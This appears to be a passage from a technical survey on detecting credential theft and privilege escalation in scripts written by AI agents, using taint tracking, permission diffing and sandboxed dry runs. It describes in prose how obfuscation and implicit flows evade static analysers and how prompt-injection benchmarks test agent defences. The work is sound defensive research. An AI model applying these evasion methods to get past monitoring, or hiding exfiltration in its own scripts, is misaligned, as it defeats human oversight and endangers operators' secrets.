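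Even within a single language, a tool can lose track of a secret when it passes through a file. Suppose the example script saved its configuration to a temporary file near line 300 and read it back near line 900. The propagation rules follow variables, and no variable links the two lines. A tool can match the lines if both contain the same fixed file name, but often can't if the script builds the name from the date. Once the script has written the secret to a file, the tool could assume that any file might contain it. In a log uploader, the tool would then put the credential label on every log the script reads afterwards and flag the upload the script was written to perform.

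The main advantage of taint tracking over a language-model reviewer on long scripts is that distance alone does not weaken the analysis. A tool can follow data across 670 lines as easily as across seven if it has a rule for every operation on the path, though a longer path is more likely to include a call that has no rule. Published tests provide little evidence about long paths because malicious packages tend to be compact. In the collection by Ryan and colleagues, an instance of malicious behaviour averages 2.17 lines.

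### Calls to a language model inside the script

A script written by an agent may itself call a language model. The example script could ask one to summarise the month's errors for the diagnostics message and include its configuration in the prompt. Whether the credentials reach line 910 then depends on what the model writes, which can't be determined from the source code.

Xu, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary*, report that CodeQL and Semgrep treat the model's answer as opaque, so any flow through the model is lost. The cautious alternative is to label the answer whenever anything in the prompt has a label. Their own tool, PRISM, sits between the two. It treats each value that the program inserts into a prompt separately, and it labels the answer only if a labelled value actually influences it:

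T(answer) = the union of T(pᵢ) over all inserted values pᵢ that reach the answer

Three language models decide which values reach the answer by comparing each value with the answer and choosing from 25 descriptions, such as "translation", "binary decision" or "ignored". A yes-or-no answer that depends on a value counts as a flow, even though it repeats none of the value's text. Another model then judges whether the answer reaches a dangerous call in the surrounding program.

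Xu and colleagues tested this on 353 pairs, each consisting of an inserted value and a dangerous call. Of these, 110 were real flows. Assuming that every pair was a flow gave 31.2% precision, 100% recall and an F1 score of 47.5%. Asking a model to judge the whole flow at once gave F1 scores between 50.0% and 62.8%. PRISM reached an F1 score of 81.7%, with 72.5% precision and 93.6% recall.

The comparison with the cautious baseline somewhat overstates PRISM's advantage, because the baseline does not check whether the model's answer ever reaches the dangerous call, as any ordinary taint tracker would. Of the 8,119 inserted values in the full collection, only 7.0% had no influence on the answer, so most of the improvement over the baseline must come from analysing the surrounding code. PRISM still has a clear advantage over asking a model the whole question at once.

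Comparing every value with every answer is also slow. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, November 2026) reports that one labelling model needs about 10,000 tokens and 13 seconds per inserted value. Their tool, also called Sightline, examines the model's internal computation instead and takes 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call.

Xu and colleagues rely on the fact that in a transformer, the design behind most language models, only attention moves information from one position in the text to another. If no chain of attention leads from an inserted value to the answer, a small change to the value cannot affect the answer. But a chain of attention doesn't prove that the value affects the answer, because models attend to much text that they don't use. The researchers therefore trained a classifier on labelled examples to tell which patterns of attention indicate real use.

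Measuring how sensitive the answer is to each value fails when the model is confident. The usual measures contain a factor of 1 − p, where p is the probability the model gave to the word it chose. If a value makes the model 99.9% sure of answering "yes", this factor is 0.001, so the measured influence is close to zero even though the value decided the answer.

The researchers tested Sightline on calls from 2,103 groups of related code repositories, using four open models. Between 12% and 14% of inserted values did not reach the answer. When set to miss about 1% of real flows, Sightline removed 43.9–65.6% of the false flows that the cautious rule creates. It also detected all 476 cases in which a model copied a planted name, number or web address word for word. These cases are the closest match to a leaked key. For models whose internals are secret, an open model can process the same text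 and detect flows about as accurately.

The 1% figure is an average over calls that resemble the ones used to set the threshold, so it is not guaranteed to hold for a prompt designed to slip a secret through. The test also used plausible reconstructions of values rather than records of real use, and language models supplied the reference labels.

A more basic obstacle is that Sightline needs the finished prompt and the model's answer, and neither exists before the script runs. It suits taint tracking during execution, or the analysis of calls that a program has already recorded. A static tool has to rely on a general assumption, and for secrets it is reasonable to be cautious and assume that the answer contains them. In the test, 86–88% of inserted values reached the answer, so labelling every answer to a prompt that contains credentials would seldom be wrong in a script with one such call.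 In a workflow that chains dozens of model calls, incorrect labels pass from each answer into the next prompt, and alarms become less useful much sooner.

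## Obfuscated data flow and control flow against static tools

Shell commands, second languages and temporary files can break the path a taint tracker follows, even when nobody intends it. Someone who wants to hide a harmful line can do the same deliberately with obfuscation, which changes how code looks but not what it does. Two theoretical results limit how well a static tool can resist obfuscation, though neither implies much about an ordinary script.

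### What the theorems rule out

Rice (1953), in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, proved that "no nontrivial class is completely recursive". In modern terms, if some programs behave in a certain way and others don't, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it behaves that way.

No tool can decide for every script whether it sends the credentials out. Given any program P that never touches the network, one can write a script that runs P and then sends the credentials. The script sends them only if P finishes, so a tool that could always decide whether a script sends the credentials could also decide whether P ever finishes. Alan Turing proved that no algorithm can do that for every program.

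Rice's theorem rules out a tool that is right about the behavior of every possible program, but not one that is right about every script a company will ever run, or one that sometimes returns "unknown". A tool can also avoid either false positives or false negatives entirely by accepting more of the other. Møller and Schwartzbach (2024), in *Static Program Analysis*, draw the usual conclusion that automated reasoning about software generally has to approximate, as the union rule in taint tracking does. The theorem does not apply to questions about a program's text, such as whether it contains a certain kind of statement.

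Proofs of this kind assume unlimited time and memory, which no real computer has. In *Detecting Traditional Packers, Decisively*, Bueno, Compton and colleagues (2013) studied programs that unpack hidden code and then run it. Detecting this behaviour is undecidable in general, but becomes decidable if the program's running time is limited. The problem is then NP-complete, which means no known method solves every case quickly.

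The second result uses that kind of difficulty to hide values from static analysis. Moser, Kruegel and Kirda (2007), in *Limits of Static Analysis for Malware Detection*, replaced fixed values in a program with computations that always give the same result but are hard to prove constant. One version relies on 3SAT, the problem of finding true-or-false values for a set of variables that satisfy a list of conditions, each involving three variables. The program contains a list of conditions that no values can satisfy and tests it on random values as it runs. The test always fails, but an analyser can determine the outcome exactly only by proving that no solution exists.

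Moser and colleagues disguised three computer worms in this way. A detector that searched for a telltale sequence of calls recognised all three worms before they were disguised and none afterwards. Two of four commercial virus scanners also missed all three disguised worms. The other two still caught two worms each, because they matched bytes in the data section, which the disguise had not changed.

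These were compiled programs, and the detector's first failure was that it could no longer locate the instructions. This would not happen with a Python script, which is source text that a parser can always read. The detector also could not identify the library functions that the worm called or confirm that two calls used the same variable, and both of these failures have counterparts in scripts.

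The proof also concerns exact answers, which a taint tracker often does not need. If the example script used such a computation to choose whether the message at line 910 contains the configuration or a harmless sentence, the tool would take the union of both branches without solving the computation, and would still raise the alarm.

Sheridan and Sherr, in *On Manufacturing Resilient Opaque Constructs Against Static Analysis*, point out that NP-hard problems are only known to be hard in the worst case, so the particular puzzle in a program may be easy. They repaired this weakness by building random puzzles with six conditions for each variable, which provably take exponential effort to refute by the standard proof method. Then they defeated their own construction. Any given set of values satisfies a random condition with probability 7/8, so for n variables it satisfies all 6n conditions with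 probability

(7/8)^(6n) ≈ 2^(−1.156n)

There are 2^n possible sets of values, so the expected number of solutions is about 2^(−0.156n). For 100 variables that is roughly 1 in 50,000. An analyser can check that the puzzle looks random, count its conditions and variables, and assume without proof that it has no solution. Sheridan and Sherr show that this takes polynomial time and, if the randomness check works, recognises every puzzle built their way. They put the chance of wrongly dismissing a solvable puzzle below 0.000006.

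That error rate is acceptable for a malware detector, though not for a compiler. The detector may not even have to solve the random logic puzzle, because a log uploader has no reason to contain one, and Sheridan and Sherr consider signs of obfuscation reasonable grounds for flagging a program.

### What each class removes from the graph

A taint tracker uses the syntax tree, the control-flow graph and the data-dependence graph, and each class of obfuscation damages a different part of these structures.

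Encoding strings doesn't change the graph's shape, but it hides what a node represents. A tool recognises the source at line 240 by the name of the credentials file. If the script encodes that name, the tool can't identify the file being read and doesn't label it, so it treats the data as clean all the way to line 910. Encoding only the outside host's address is less effective, because the tool can still trace the path from line 240 to line 910, and a rule that treats every web request as a sink still fires. The tool can often undo a fixed encoding by computing the result itself. It could also treat every unknown file as sensitive, but this would include the logs if the script builds their names from the date.

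When a program chooses its calls at run time, the graph lacks the link between a call and the function it reaches. At line 910 the tool would find labelled data going into an unidentified function. Under the usual default rule, the tool labels the function's result but raises no alarm, because it cannot identify the function as a sink. Harmless programs also choose functions this way, for example to pick the right reader for each file type. If the choices are in a fixed table, the tool can check every entry. If the name comes from outside the script, the tool has to either ignore the call or assume it could reach any function.

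Code generated at run time hinders static tools most. When a script assembles text and executes it as code, the syntax tree contains the instruction to execute the text but not the statements that will run, and a code slice (the part of a program that bears on one data flow) may be empty. However, the instruction is usually easy to find, and a tool can flag it without knowing what the text will contain.

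Control-flow flattening hides the order in which statements run. It splits the code into blocks and puts them in a loop, where a changing number selects the next block. In the control-flow graph, almost any block can then follow any other, which defeats a detector that looks for one call followed by another. A conservative taint tracker still finds the flow to line 910 because it covers every order, including the real one. But it also covers orders that never happen. If the script uses the same variable first for the credentials and later for a file name, the tool can no longer determine that the second value replaced the first, so it raises more false alarms.

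### Implicit flow

The fifth class, implicit flow, passes information through the choice of branch, a connection that the data-dependence graph never contained. A single bit is enough to show the problem:

| Statement | Label on "copy", usual rules | Label on "copy", branches tracked |
|---|---|---|
| copy = 0 | none | none |
| if secret_bit == 1: copy = 1 | none | secret |
| send(copy) | no alarm | alarm |

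After the second statement, copy always equals secret_bit. But copy has no label, because the program assigned it only constants, and constants have no label. A loop that does the same for every bit of a key produces a complete, unlabelled copy of the key.

The repair is to add the labels of the conditions that decide whether a statement runs:

T(x) = T(assigned value) ∪ T(conditions that control the assignment)

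This catches the copied bit, but it also labels most of an ordinary script. Suppose the example script checks at line 245 whether the credentials file is empty, and stops if it is. Everything after line 245 runs only if the check succeeds, so a strict tool labels the archive, the count for the metrics host and every progress message. The upload at line 655 then raises an alarm, although it reveals only that the credentials file was not empty, which nobody needs to keep secret. Most scripts that log in somewhere contain a check like this.

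Tool builders have mostly left out implicit flows. *Implicit flows* (King, Hicks and colleagues, 2008) observes that the tools that had succeeded in finding security violations focused on explicit flows. In *An empirical study of information flows in real-world Javascript*, Staicu, Schoepe and colleagues found a lightweight taint analysis sufficient for most of the security problems they studied, although some privacy-related code required tracking implicit flows through branches that ran. They found no evidence that tracking "hidden" implicit flows, where information leaks because a branch did not run, revealed any security problem that simpler methods missed.

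That is good evidence about code that wasn't written to defeat a taint tracker, but little evidence about code from a hijacked or misaligned model that knows the tracker is there. An operator could settle for flagging only branches that test individual characters or bits of a secret, since a log uploader has to check whether its key works but doesn't need to examine its parts.

### Detection rates on obfuscated packages

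The npm study provides the best figures on how often attackers use these methods. Guo and colleagues searched the malicious packages with 53 pattern rules for eight categories of evasion, and an expert reviewed every match. They found that 80.3% of the packages used no evasion. The most common technique was string obfuscation, which appeared in 541 packages. The researchers attribute the low rate of evasion to the registry's lack of scanning before publication, which lets simple attacks succeed.

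The true share of evasive packages may be higher, because evasion that matches none of the 53 rules isn't counted and the collection contains only malware that somebody eventually caught. The explanation is also little reassurance to an operator who reviews every script, since an attacker who expects a review has more reason to hide malicious code.

Three learned classifiers, SAP_DT, SAP_RF and Cerebro, each caught at most 26.6% of the packages with string obfuscation. Their features come from the surface of the code, and renaming variables or scrambling text changes that surface directly. Packj's static mode caught 86.0%, and Guo and colleagues attribute this to its reliance on the calls a package makes, regardless of names.

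The comparison makes Packj look better than it is, because Packj flagged popular harmless packages about as often as string-obfuscated malicious ones, at a rate of about 86%. OSSGadget, a pattern matcher, detected an average of 81.2% of malicious packages across the eight kinds of evasion, but its published precision and recall imply that it also flagged about 79% of harmless ones. IntelGuard, the language-model pipeline with retrieval, detected an average of 81.3%, and at least 66.7% for every technique, while flagging only 1.5% of harmless packages. This suggests that a language-model reviewer with good reference material can be a useful second check on obfuscated code.

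GuardDog, the taint-tracking scanner that did well overall, caught only 7% of the 149 packages that build and execute code at run time. Guo and colleagues classify generating and executing code this way as a malicious behaviour rather than an evasion technique, and explain that GuardDog's rules were not designed to cover it, so the figure measures a gap in one rule set. A rule that flags every instruction to execute generated text would catch many more of these packages, but it would also flag harmless programs that do the same.

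Packages with two or three obfuscation techniques set off fewer detectors than packages with one, but those with four or more set off the most. Heavy obfuscation leaves its own traces, such as random-looking text and large blocks of decoding code. A careful attacker would therefore use just enough obfuscation to break one link in the path, which may be enough to make a taint tracker miss the flow.

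### Refusing code that a tool cannot analyse

A public registry cannot simply ban obfuscation. Moser and colleagues note that developers also use it legitimately, to protect intellectual property. In the npm study, long runs of encoded text were more common in harmless packages than in malicious ones.

An organisation that runs its own model's scripts is in a stronger position. No trade secrets need to be hidden from the organisation, and the model can rewrite a rejected script in seconds, so the organisation can refuse any code that its tools cannot analyse. For the example script, such a rule might require that every function call uses a plain name, that no text is turned into code, and that network destinations appear as constants. These requirements concern the script's text rather than its behaviour, so Rice's theorem does not prevent a tool from checking them. The rule will also reject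 some harmless scripts.

The rule could also prevent most implicit flows. If the script may pass credentials only to an approved login function, and may not read, compare or copy them itself, it cannot branch on their contents. The cloud provider's library would then have to open the file, replacing the read at line 240. The script could still learn whether the login succeeded, which is the only bit it needs.

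Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues (2026), in *STELP*, built a system of this kind for Python at the bank Capital One. It handles a script in four stages:

1. It parses the code into a syntax tree and compares the tree with a list of permitted language features.
2. It executes the code one statement at a time, checking each call against lists of permitted functions and imports, and enforcing limits on time, loops and nesting.
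3. It sends calls to outside tools through a separate proxy service.
4. If it stops the code, a language model turns the error into advice, and the model that wrote the code tries again.

STELP checks each call as it happens, so computing a function's name at run time doesn't hide the call from it. But by the time STELP blocks a call, the statements before it have already run. If the operator allowed web requests but not policy changes, STELP would stop the example script at line 1,060, after line 910 had sent the credentials.

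For the test, Shinde and colleagues had the model Llama 3.3 70B insert flaws into 164 short programming exercises. After human reviewers checked the results, 470 unsafe versions remained. CodeShield is Meta's pattern-based static checker.

| System | Unsafe samples blocked | Safe samples allowed |
|---|---|---|
| STELP | 100% | 98.1% |
| CodeShield | 68% | 93% |

The perfect score depends heavily on the configuration. Shinde and colleagues started from the minimum permissions that the safe samples needed to run, so almost anything added to an exercise would break a rule. Of the 470 blocks, 311 were for calls to functions not on the list. The samples also differ from the example script. About 200 of the unsafe ones contain endless loops, deadlocks or wasted resources, and none of the 12 categories of flaw covers stealing credentials.

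The configuration allows eight imports from Python's standard library, including those for mathematics and text patterns. It provides no function for opening files and no network access. It stops a program after 200 milliseconds or 100,000 loop iterations, and processing a month of web-server logs could easily exceed these limits. The example script could not do any of its work under these rules, even without the harmful lines.

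Shinde and colleagues also compared STELP's output with normal Python's on 361 programs, and STELP's was correct every time. But they had selected programs that fitted the configuration, so the test does not measure how many useful scripts the configuration would reject.

An operator would therefore have to add files, compression, the cloud library and some form of network access. A general function for web requests would make line 910 acceptable again. Narrow functions would be safer, such as one that uploads an archive to the company's bucket and one that posts a number to the metrics host, with both destinations fixed outside the script. Line 910 would then have no permitted call to make, although the script could still hide secrets inside the archive. Someone has to write and maintain these functions for every kind of task, which is probably a bigger burden than the delay STELP adds.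 In a test on short programs, that delay was a median of 0.19 milliseconds per program and 520 milliseconds in the worst case.

Refusals are less of a problem when the model can rewrite the rejected code. In the test, 90.2% of the rejected samples passed after fewer than two retries, though about 8% needed more than ten. These were small exercises, and repairing a 1,200-line script may be harder. A model with a harmful aim can also learn from the advice which constructs get through, so an operator should keep the rejected versions and have someone review them as well as the one that passed.

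### Harmful code in plain form

A rule against code that resists analysis doesn't stop harmful code that is easy to read. Even without such a rule, malicious npm packages became simpler between 2021 and 2023, and SAP_DT's detection rate fell from 87.15% to 39.49%. Guo and colleagues explain that the classifier had learned to associate malware with encoded, random-looking text, which attackers were using less. In 21.2% of all the malicious packages, the entire attack was in the installation commands, which can look exactly like those of a normal build.

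An overeager or mistaken model has no reason to disguise its code, so its harmful lines will usually be plain too. In the example script, line 910 sends an ordinary message through an ordinary web library. A taint tracker can still catch it, because it can follow the data from the credentials to that line.

Line 1,060 is even plainer, and taint tracking does not help because the line involves no secret. Many legitimate administration scripts contain the same line. A list of permitted functions would stop it only if someone had already worked out which cloud operations a log uploader needs.

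## Permission diffing: what a script can do against what its task needs

Permission diffing compares a script with exactly such a list. An analyser takes the script's effective capabilities, E, and removes the required capabilities, R:

excess = E \ R

The backslash means "without", so the excess is everything in E that is not in R. For the example script, the comparison might look like this:

| Capability | In E because of | In R? | Result |
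|---|---|---|---|
| Read the web-server logs | the compression step | yes | no excess |
| Read the credentials file | line 240 | yes | no excess |
| Write to the log bucket | line 655 | yes | no excess |
| Post to the metrics host | the final count | yes | no excess |
| Send data to an outside host | line 910 | no | excess |
| Attach policies to its own account | line 1,060 | no | excess |
| Perform any action in the cloud account | the policy attached at line 1,060 | no | excess |

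The upload needs the credentials, so reading them is not an excess permission. The comparison catches line 1,060, which taint tracking misses. It also catches line 910 without tracing what the message contains.

Now suppose the script makes neither of those calls, but adds the credentials to the log archive and uploads the archive to the permitted bucket. The task requires both reading the credentials file and writing to that bucket, so the permission diff is empty. The theft is visible only in the data flow from the credentials file into the archive.

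Excess permissions do not prove bad intent. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a test of 11 agents in 544 scenarios, in which 6 chose a tool with more privilege than they needed in over 30% of cases.

### What the script can do

An analyser first maps each call to the permission it needs. *Android Permissions Demystified* (Felt, Chin and colleagues, 2011) did this for Android, where an app had to request its permissions at installation. The paper's tool, Stowaway, finds the calls an app makes to Android's programming interface, looks up the permission each one needs, and subtracts those permissions from the ones the app requested. About a third of the 940 apps tested had requested more permissions than their code used.

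Stowaway infers the permissions a program needs from its code, which works for checking whether a developer requested too many. It would give the wrong answer for the example script. Line 1,060 uses the permission to attach policies, so Stowaway would count that permission as needed and report no excess. When the code is under suspicion, R has to come from another source.

A script also gains capabilities from the libraries it calls. Google's *Capslock* (2023) reports how Go packages reach privileged operations in the standard library. It follows calls through intermediate functions, so a package that never opens a network connection itself is still reported as having network access if a function it calls leads to one. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* lists an experimental version for Rust and one for Java that works on compiled packages without their source code.

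The analyser has to start from the functions the script calls. AWS's library can perform many cloud operations, so an analyser that counted the whole library would report that any script using it to upload a file can also change policies.

The calls determine what a script will attempt, and the rights of its account determine which attempts succeed. If C is the set of permissions that the calls use and A is the set that the account holds, the script starts with the permissions that are in both:

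E₀ = C ∩ A

The analyser has to read the script's rights (A) from the cloud account, because the script does not contain them. These rights can be very broad. Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Flaw in AWS Bedrock Code Interpreter Raises Alarms* reports that the default role in a starter kit for AWS's agent service can include full access to a database service and to all stored secrets, plus read access to every storage bucket in the account.

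If the example script's account lacks the right to attach policies, line 1,060 fails and E₀ doesn't include that right. The attempt is still a good reason to distrust the script, so the analyser should also report C \ R.

The set A \ R is also useful, because whoever receives the credentials from line 910 can use every right in A, including those the script never uses. *The Vulnerability With No CVE* (2026) proposes treating this kind of gap between an agent's task and its authority as a vulnerability with its own record. The record stays open until, for example, someone narrows the authority, adds a missing control or accepts the risk.

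Some rights let their holder obtain others, and privilege escalation shows up fully only when the analyser adds these:

Eₙ₊₁ = Eₙ ∪ gain(Eₙ)

Here gain(Eₙ) is the set of rights that someone holding Eₙ could obtain. The analyser repeats the step until a round adds nothing. In the example, E₀ contains the right to attach policies to the service account, and the first round adds every action in the cloud account.

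The route can be longer. Suppose the script can only switch to a deployment role, which can edit policies. The first round adds the deployment role's rights and the second adds everything else. An analyser that searches only E₀ for administrator rights would find none.

Attack graphs similarly map what an intruder could reach after breaking into one machine. *PRISM* (2026), a paper on agents' tool privileges (not the taint tracker of the same name), points out that attack graphs describe fixed networks and do not handle agents that choose their calls as they run. A finished script is easier to analyze because most of its calls are already in the text.

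### Comparing two policies

Access policies contain wildcards and conditions, so one rule can cover an unlimited number of requests, and a tool cannot find the difference between two policies by listing what each one allows. An SMT solver, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of logical conditions, can look for a request that the first policy allows and the second denies. If no such request exists, the difference is empty.

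*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a solver in this way for policies that govern an agent's tools. The same search works for the policy languages of AWS, Microsoft Azure and Google Cloud wherever a tool can translate the rules into logical conditions.

This comparison can detect the problem in the log-reader case, where an innocent-looking script attaches a company policy that someone has edited to add administrator rights. A solver that compares the policy's current version with the last approved one would return a request that only the new version allows, such as one to delete a database.

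### What the task needs

The simplest source for R is a manifest, the list of capabilities that a program's author declares. It is easy to check but only as reliable as its author. If the model that wrote the example script also wrote the manifest, it could declare that the script sends diagnostics to an outside host, and line 910 would pass the check.

An earlier version of the program is a better standard, if that version was harmless. Google suggests using Capslock to alert developers when a package's capabilities change unexpectedly. McClintock (2025) argues in *Trust but Verify* that comparing advertised permissions with actual ones can stop attacks such as the malicious version of the Go package boltdb-go. Comparing versions suits recurring tasks, such as a log uploader that a model writes anew every month. The code may differ each time, but the capabilities should stay the same.

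Records of past runs show what a script used, which may be more than it needed. If last month's script also contacted the outside host, that host would be in R. *PRISM* makes this objection to methods that fit policies to past authorization records, and adds that a new agent has no record. Records can also omit permissions that a task rarely uses, such as those for a yearly clean-up.

An operator can test more directly whether a task needs a permission by removing it and checking whether the task still succeeds. *Aletheia* (2026) does this for the permissions that a code repository's rules request for coding agents. It runs the task in a full sandbox and in restricted ones with individual permissions removed.

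*SkillScope* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tests individual actions in agent skills. A language model writes sample tasks for a skill, and SkillScope runs each task twice, once normally and once with the suspect action disabled. Models then judge whether the second run still met the user's goal and whether the request authorised the action. SkillScope reports the action as over-privileged if it was unnecessary or unauthorised.

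In the example, the test separates the harmful lines, 910 and 1,060, from the ordinary line 240. Disabling either harmful line leaves the upload and the count intact, while disabling line 240 breaks the upload.

SkillScope had an F1 score of 94.53% on 200 hand-labelled skills, half of them over-privileged. Among 68,312 skills from public marketplaces, it confirmed over-privileged actions in 6,590, or nearly 10%. Wu and colleagues describe one real skill that was supposed to track work sessions locally and draw a chart. It also contained instructions for the agent to send the report to an outside Telegram account and to collect and send out network settings and command history.

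Some tasks have no single correct R. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) found that the smallest sufficient set of permissions was not unique for 29.8–33.3% of tasks in Microsoft Graph, Microsoft's interface to its office services, and for 3.2% of tasks in Google's services. The alternatives always authorised different operations.

The log uploader might post its count directly to the metrics host or through a monitoring service. If R, the set of permissions the task needs, contains only one route, a harmless script that takes the other raises a false alarm. If R contains both, every script gets a permission it does not need. The analyser should instead keep a separate set for each route and accept a script that fits within either one. Removal tests can also mislead here, because if a script uses both routes, disabling either one still lets the task finish, so both look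 unnecessary.

### Policies derived from the task by a language model

In Progent, a language model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of available tools, before the agent has read any outside content. A model that wrote a script's policy this way would not read the code, so a misleading comment or function name could not influence the policy.

Each rule in a Progent policy names a tool and can limit its arguments, for example by allowing Slack messages only to one person. Progent blocks calls that match no rule. As the agent learns more, the model proposes policy updates, and a solver compares the new policy with the old one. Progent applies an update automatically if it allows nothing that the old policy blocked, and otherwise asks for approval. In the tests, only 6% of updates needed approval.

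Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants instructions meant to hijack an agent doing banking, travel, messaging and office tasks. GPT-4o ran the agent and wrote the policies. The share of successful attacks fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, with no significant loss in completed tasks. On a second benchmark, ASB, it fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the attacks that still worked on ASB used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of harmless ones.

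The tests assumed a user who approved every expansion, so careful approval cannot explain the improvement. Without updates, the first policy cut successful attacks on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Still, *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that hostile text in a tool's results may lead the model to loosen the policy during an update. The solver detects such a change, but a user who approves everything will let it through.

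These agents called their tools one at a time. If an agent's tool is "run this Python file", the whole example script is a single call, and a policy on tool calls cannot treat line 655 differently from line 910. An operator would have to apply the policy to the functions the script calls.

A low attack rate also does not show that a policy is tight, because the agent may never attempt the calls that the policy wrongly allows. Sharma, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *Ajar*, therefore tested the defences directly. From AgentDojo's 97 harmless tasks they generated 10,471 tests, each proposing one call at a particular point in a task, and recorded whether the defence allowed it. Their main measure weights each unneeded call by the harm it could do:

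leakage = weight of unneeded calls allowed ÷ weight of all unneeded calls proposed

A reversible read of the user's own data has a weight of 1, and an irreversible payment has a weight of 27. A defence that refuses everything has no leakage, so Sharma and colleagues also measured the share of required calls that each defence allowed. These are the results with Claude Sonnet 5 making the decisions:

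| Defence | Leakage | Required calls allowed | Planted attacks allowed |
|---|---|---|---|
| List of needed tools, any arguments | 35.5% | 100% | 99 of 609 |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 30.1% | not measured | 74 of 581 |
| AC4A | 11.1% | 71.5% | 46 of 609 |
| Progent | 10.3% | 90.2% | 34 of 609 |
| CaMeL | 9.0% | 70.0% | 16 of 609 |
| Permission Assistant | 8.1% | 96.1% | 25 of 609 |
| List of needed tools with exact arguments | 0.2% | 91% | 1 of 609 |

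The researchers built the two lists from the benchmark's own solutions to serve as reference points. In AC4A and Progent, a model writes a policy. In CaMeL, the model writes a program and the system checks its data flows. In Permission Assistant and auto mode, a model judges each call.

Progent allowed 5.6% of the planted attacks in Sharma and colleagues' test, whereas 1.0% of attacks succeeded in its own test. The two tests used different models, and an attack counts as successful only if the agent also attempts it. Progent's policy also tightens as a task proceeds, and the 5.6% figure counts each call once, at the earliest step. When Sharma and colleagues counted every proposal at every step, Progent allowed 3.4%.

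Auto mode's leakage is high partly because it is designed to block only actions that are irreversible, destructive or aimed outside the user's declared environment, and many unneeded calls are none of these. It also interfered little with ordinary work. Agents completed 89.0% of harmless tasks with auto mode and 92.4% without it, whereas AC4A reduced completion from 85.6% to 50.5%. The comparison isn't exact, because auto mode could be tested only on calls that its agent agreed to make.

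The confidence intervals of the other four defences overlap, so their ranking is uncertain. AgentDojo's checks confirmed only 27% of the labels, and the rest depend on the researchers' rules for what a task needs.

Models make similar mistakes with files. In *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?*, Yan, Weng and colleagues (2026) asked models which files each of 120 terminal tasks had to read, write or execute. Leading models often omitted permissions that the task needed while granting sensitive ones it didn't need. More reasoning only made each model more consistent in its own kind of error.

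The model first simulated the task and listed everything it would access, then checked whether each entry was justified. Splitting the work into these two steps improved success on sensitive tasks by up to 15.8% for models that had been too strict, and it reduced successful attacks for every model tested.

If R, the set of permissions the task needs, omits a needed permission, the diff raises a false alarm, and if R includes an unneeded one, the diff hides any harmful use of it. For example, if the model wrongly includes policy changes in R for a log uploader, the diff no longer reports the policy change on line 1,060 as excess. Rashidi found that every enforcement mechanism in the 39 surveyed papers assumed an honest policy author and did not address mistakes in writing policies. For a recurring task, a person can check R once and reuse it, which takes far less time than reading 1,200 lines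 of script every month.

### Packj and the cost of subtracting nothing

Packj's static mode works out a package's effective capabilities but doesn't estimate which ones the package needs. It sorts its 56 listed calls into 10 permission groups and flags any package that uses one of them, in effect treating R, the set of needed permissions, as empty. That is why it caught 98.69% of the malware in the npm study by Guo and colleagues but had a precision of only 50.41%.

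Flagging every package in that test would have given 100% recall and 46.8% precision, and Packj did little better. If one script in a thousand were harmful and the error rates stayed the same, only about one alarm in 870 would be real.

Packj's static mode also caught every package that used anti-analysis techniques, which are designed to detect or resist inspection. Guo and colleagues credit this to monitoring system calls at the operating-system level. That explanation does not fit a static mode, which does not run the package and so has no system calls to monitor.

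Packj's perfect score on these techniques is no evidence that it resists evasion, because flagging nearly everything is enough to explain it. Only 42 packages used the techniques, and a tool that flagged a random 98.69% of malicious packages would have a 0.9869⁴² ≈ 57% chance of catching all of them.

The same map of calls could be useful with a good estimate of R. A call that opens a network connection would then raise an alarm in a package that only formats text, but not in a web client, which needs such connections.

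### Where the subtraction fails

Permission groups such as "files" and "network" are too coarse for the example script. The upload needs the network, so "network" belongs in R, and the message to the outside host no longer counts as excess. Sharma and colleagues describe a banking task that must change the amount of standing order 7, the user's rent. A planted instruction is meant to redirect standing order 6 to an attacker's account. Both calls use the same tool, so a policy that lists only tool names must allow both or refuse both.

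*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) argues that least privilege must also cover a call's arguments, the data it returns and the authority an agent passes to its subordinates. This delegated authority matters for scripts that direct many agents. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) points out that a single policy for a whole task cannot give two agents different authority, so an agent that only summarises logs would also be allowed to upload them.

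Finer permissions leave less room for abuse but are harder to get right. In the AgentDojo test, the researchers wrote the exact-argument list from the known solutions, and it still blocked about 9% of the calls that a typical task required.

Calls that start another program cause a more serious problem, because that program can use any right the script's account holds. If the analyser adds all those rights to E, every script that runs a shell command has a large excess. If it treats "run a command" as one permission and the task needs a command, the excess is empty whatever the command does. When the command is fixed text, the analyser can do better by parsing it and working out its capabilities separately.

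Listing forbidden commands is a poor substitute for permission diffing. Rashidi describes a test of 1,709 such lists from GitHub, in which a language model proposed ways to bypass them and a sandbox checked whether the bypasses worked. Depending on the type of bypass, between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists were fragile.

Code assembled at run time creates the same choice. The analyser cannot map calls that are not yet in the text, so either it must assume that the code could use every right in A, or the operator must reject the script.

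A script can also get a trusted service to act for it. Suppose the example script cannot open a certain file but can ask a file-management service to copy it. The script's own permissions include only the call to the service, and the service opens the file with its own rights. E is then too small unless the analyser adds everything the service will do for a caller.

*My Credentials, Please* (2026) looks for this weakness in MCP servers, programs that offer tools to agents. Its scanner estimates which files each tool needs for its legitimate job. A language model drafts this estimate, and the scanner adds the libraries and system files the tool needs to run.

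A tool that adds files to a Git repository needs read and write access to the working directory and read-only access to its dependencies. The scanner places test credentials outside both areas and checks in a sandbox whether a request can make the tool reach them. If the credentials were only outside the working directory, they could still be among the files the tool is allowed to read.

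## Sandboxed dry runs: running the script and recording what it does

An operator can use planted test credentials to check a whole script as well as a single tool. In a sandboxed dry run, the script executes in an isolated copy of its usual environment, with false credentials and a simulated network, while a recorder logs what it does. Encoded file names, functions chosen at run time and generated code hinder static tools, but running the script turns them into actual files, calls and statements that the recorder can log.

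A sandboxed dry run executes the real code and relies on isolation to prevent harm. This differs from the "plan" or "dry run" option in many administration tools. Terraform, for example, which sets up cloud infrastructure, can list the changes it would make without making them. Terraform itself produces that list, so the list is only as trustworthy as the program. If a model gave the example script its own dry-run option, the option might skip the upload but still send the message at line 910.

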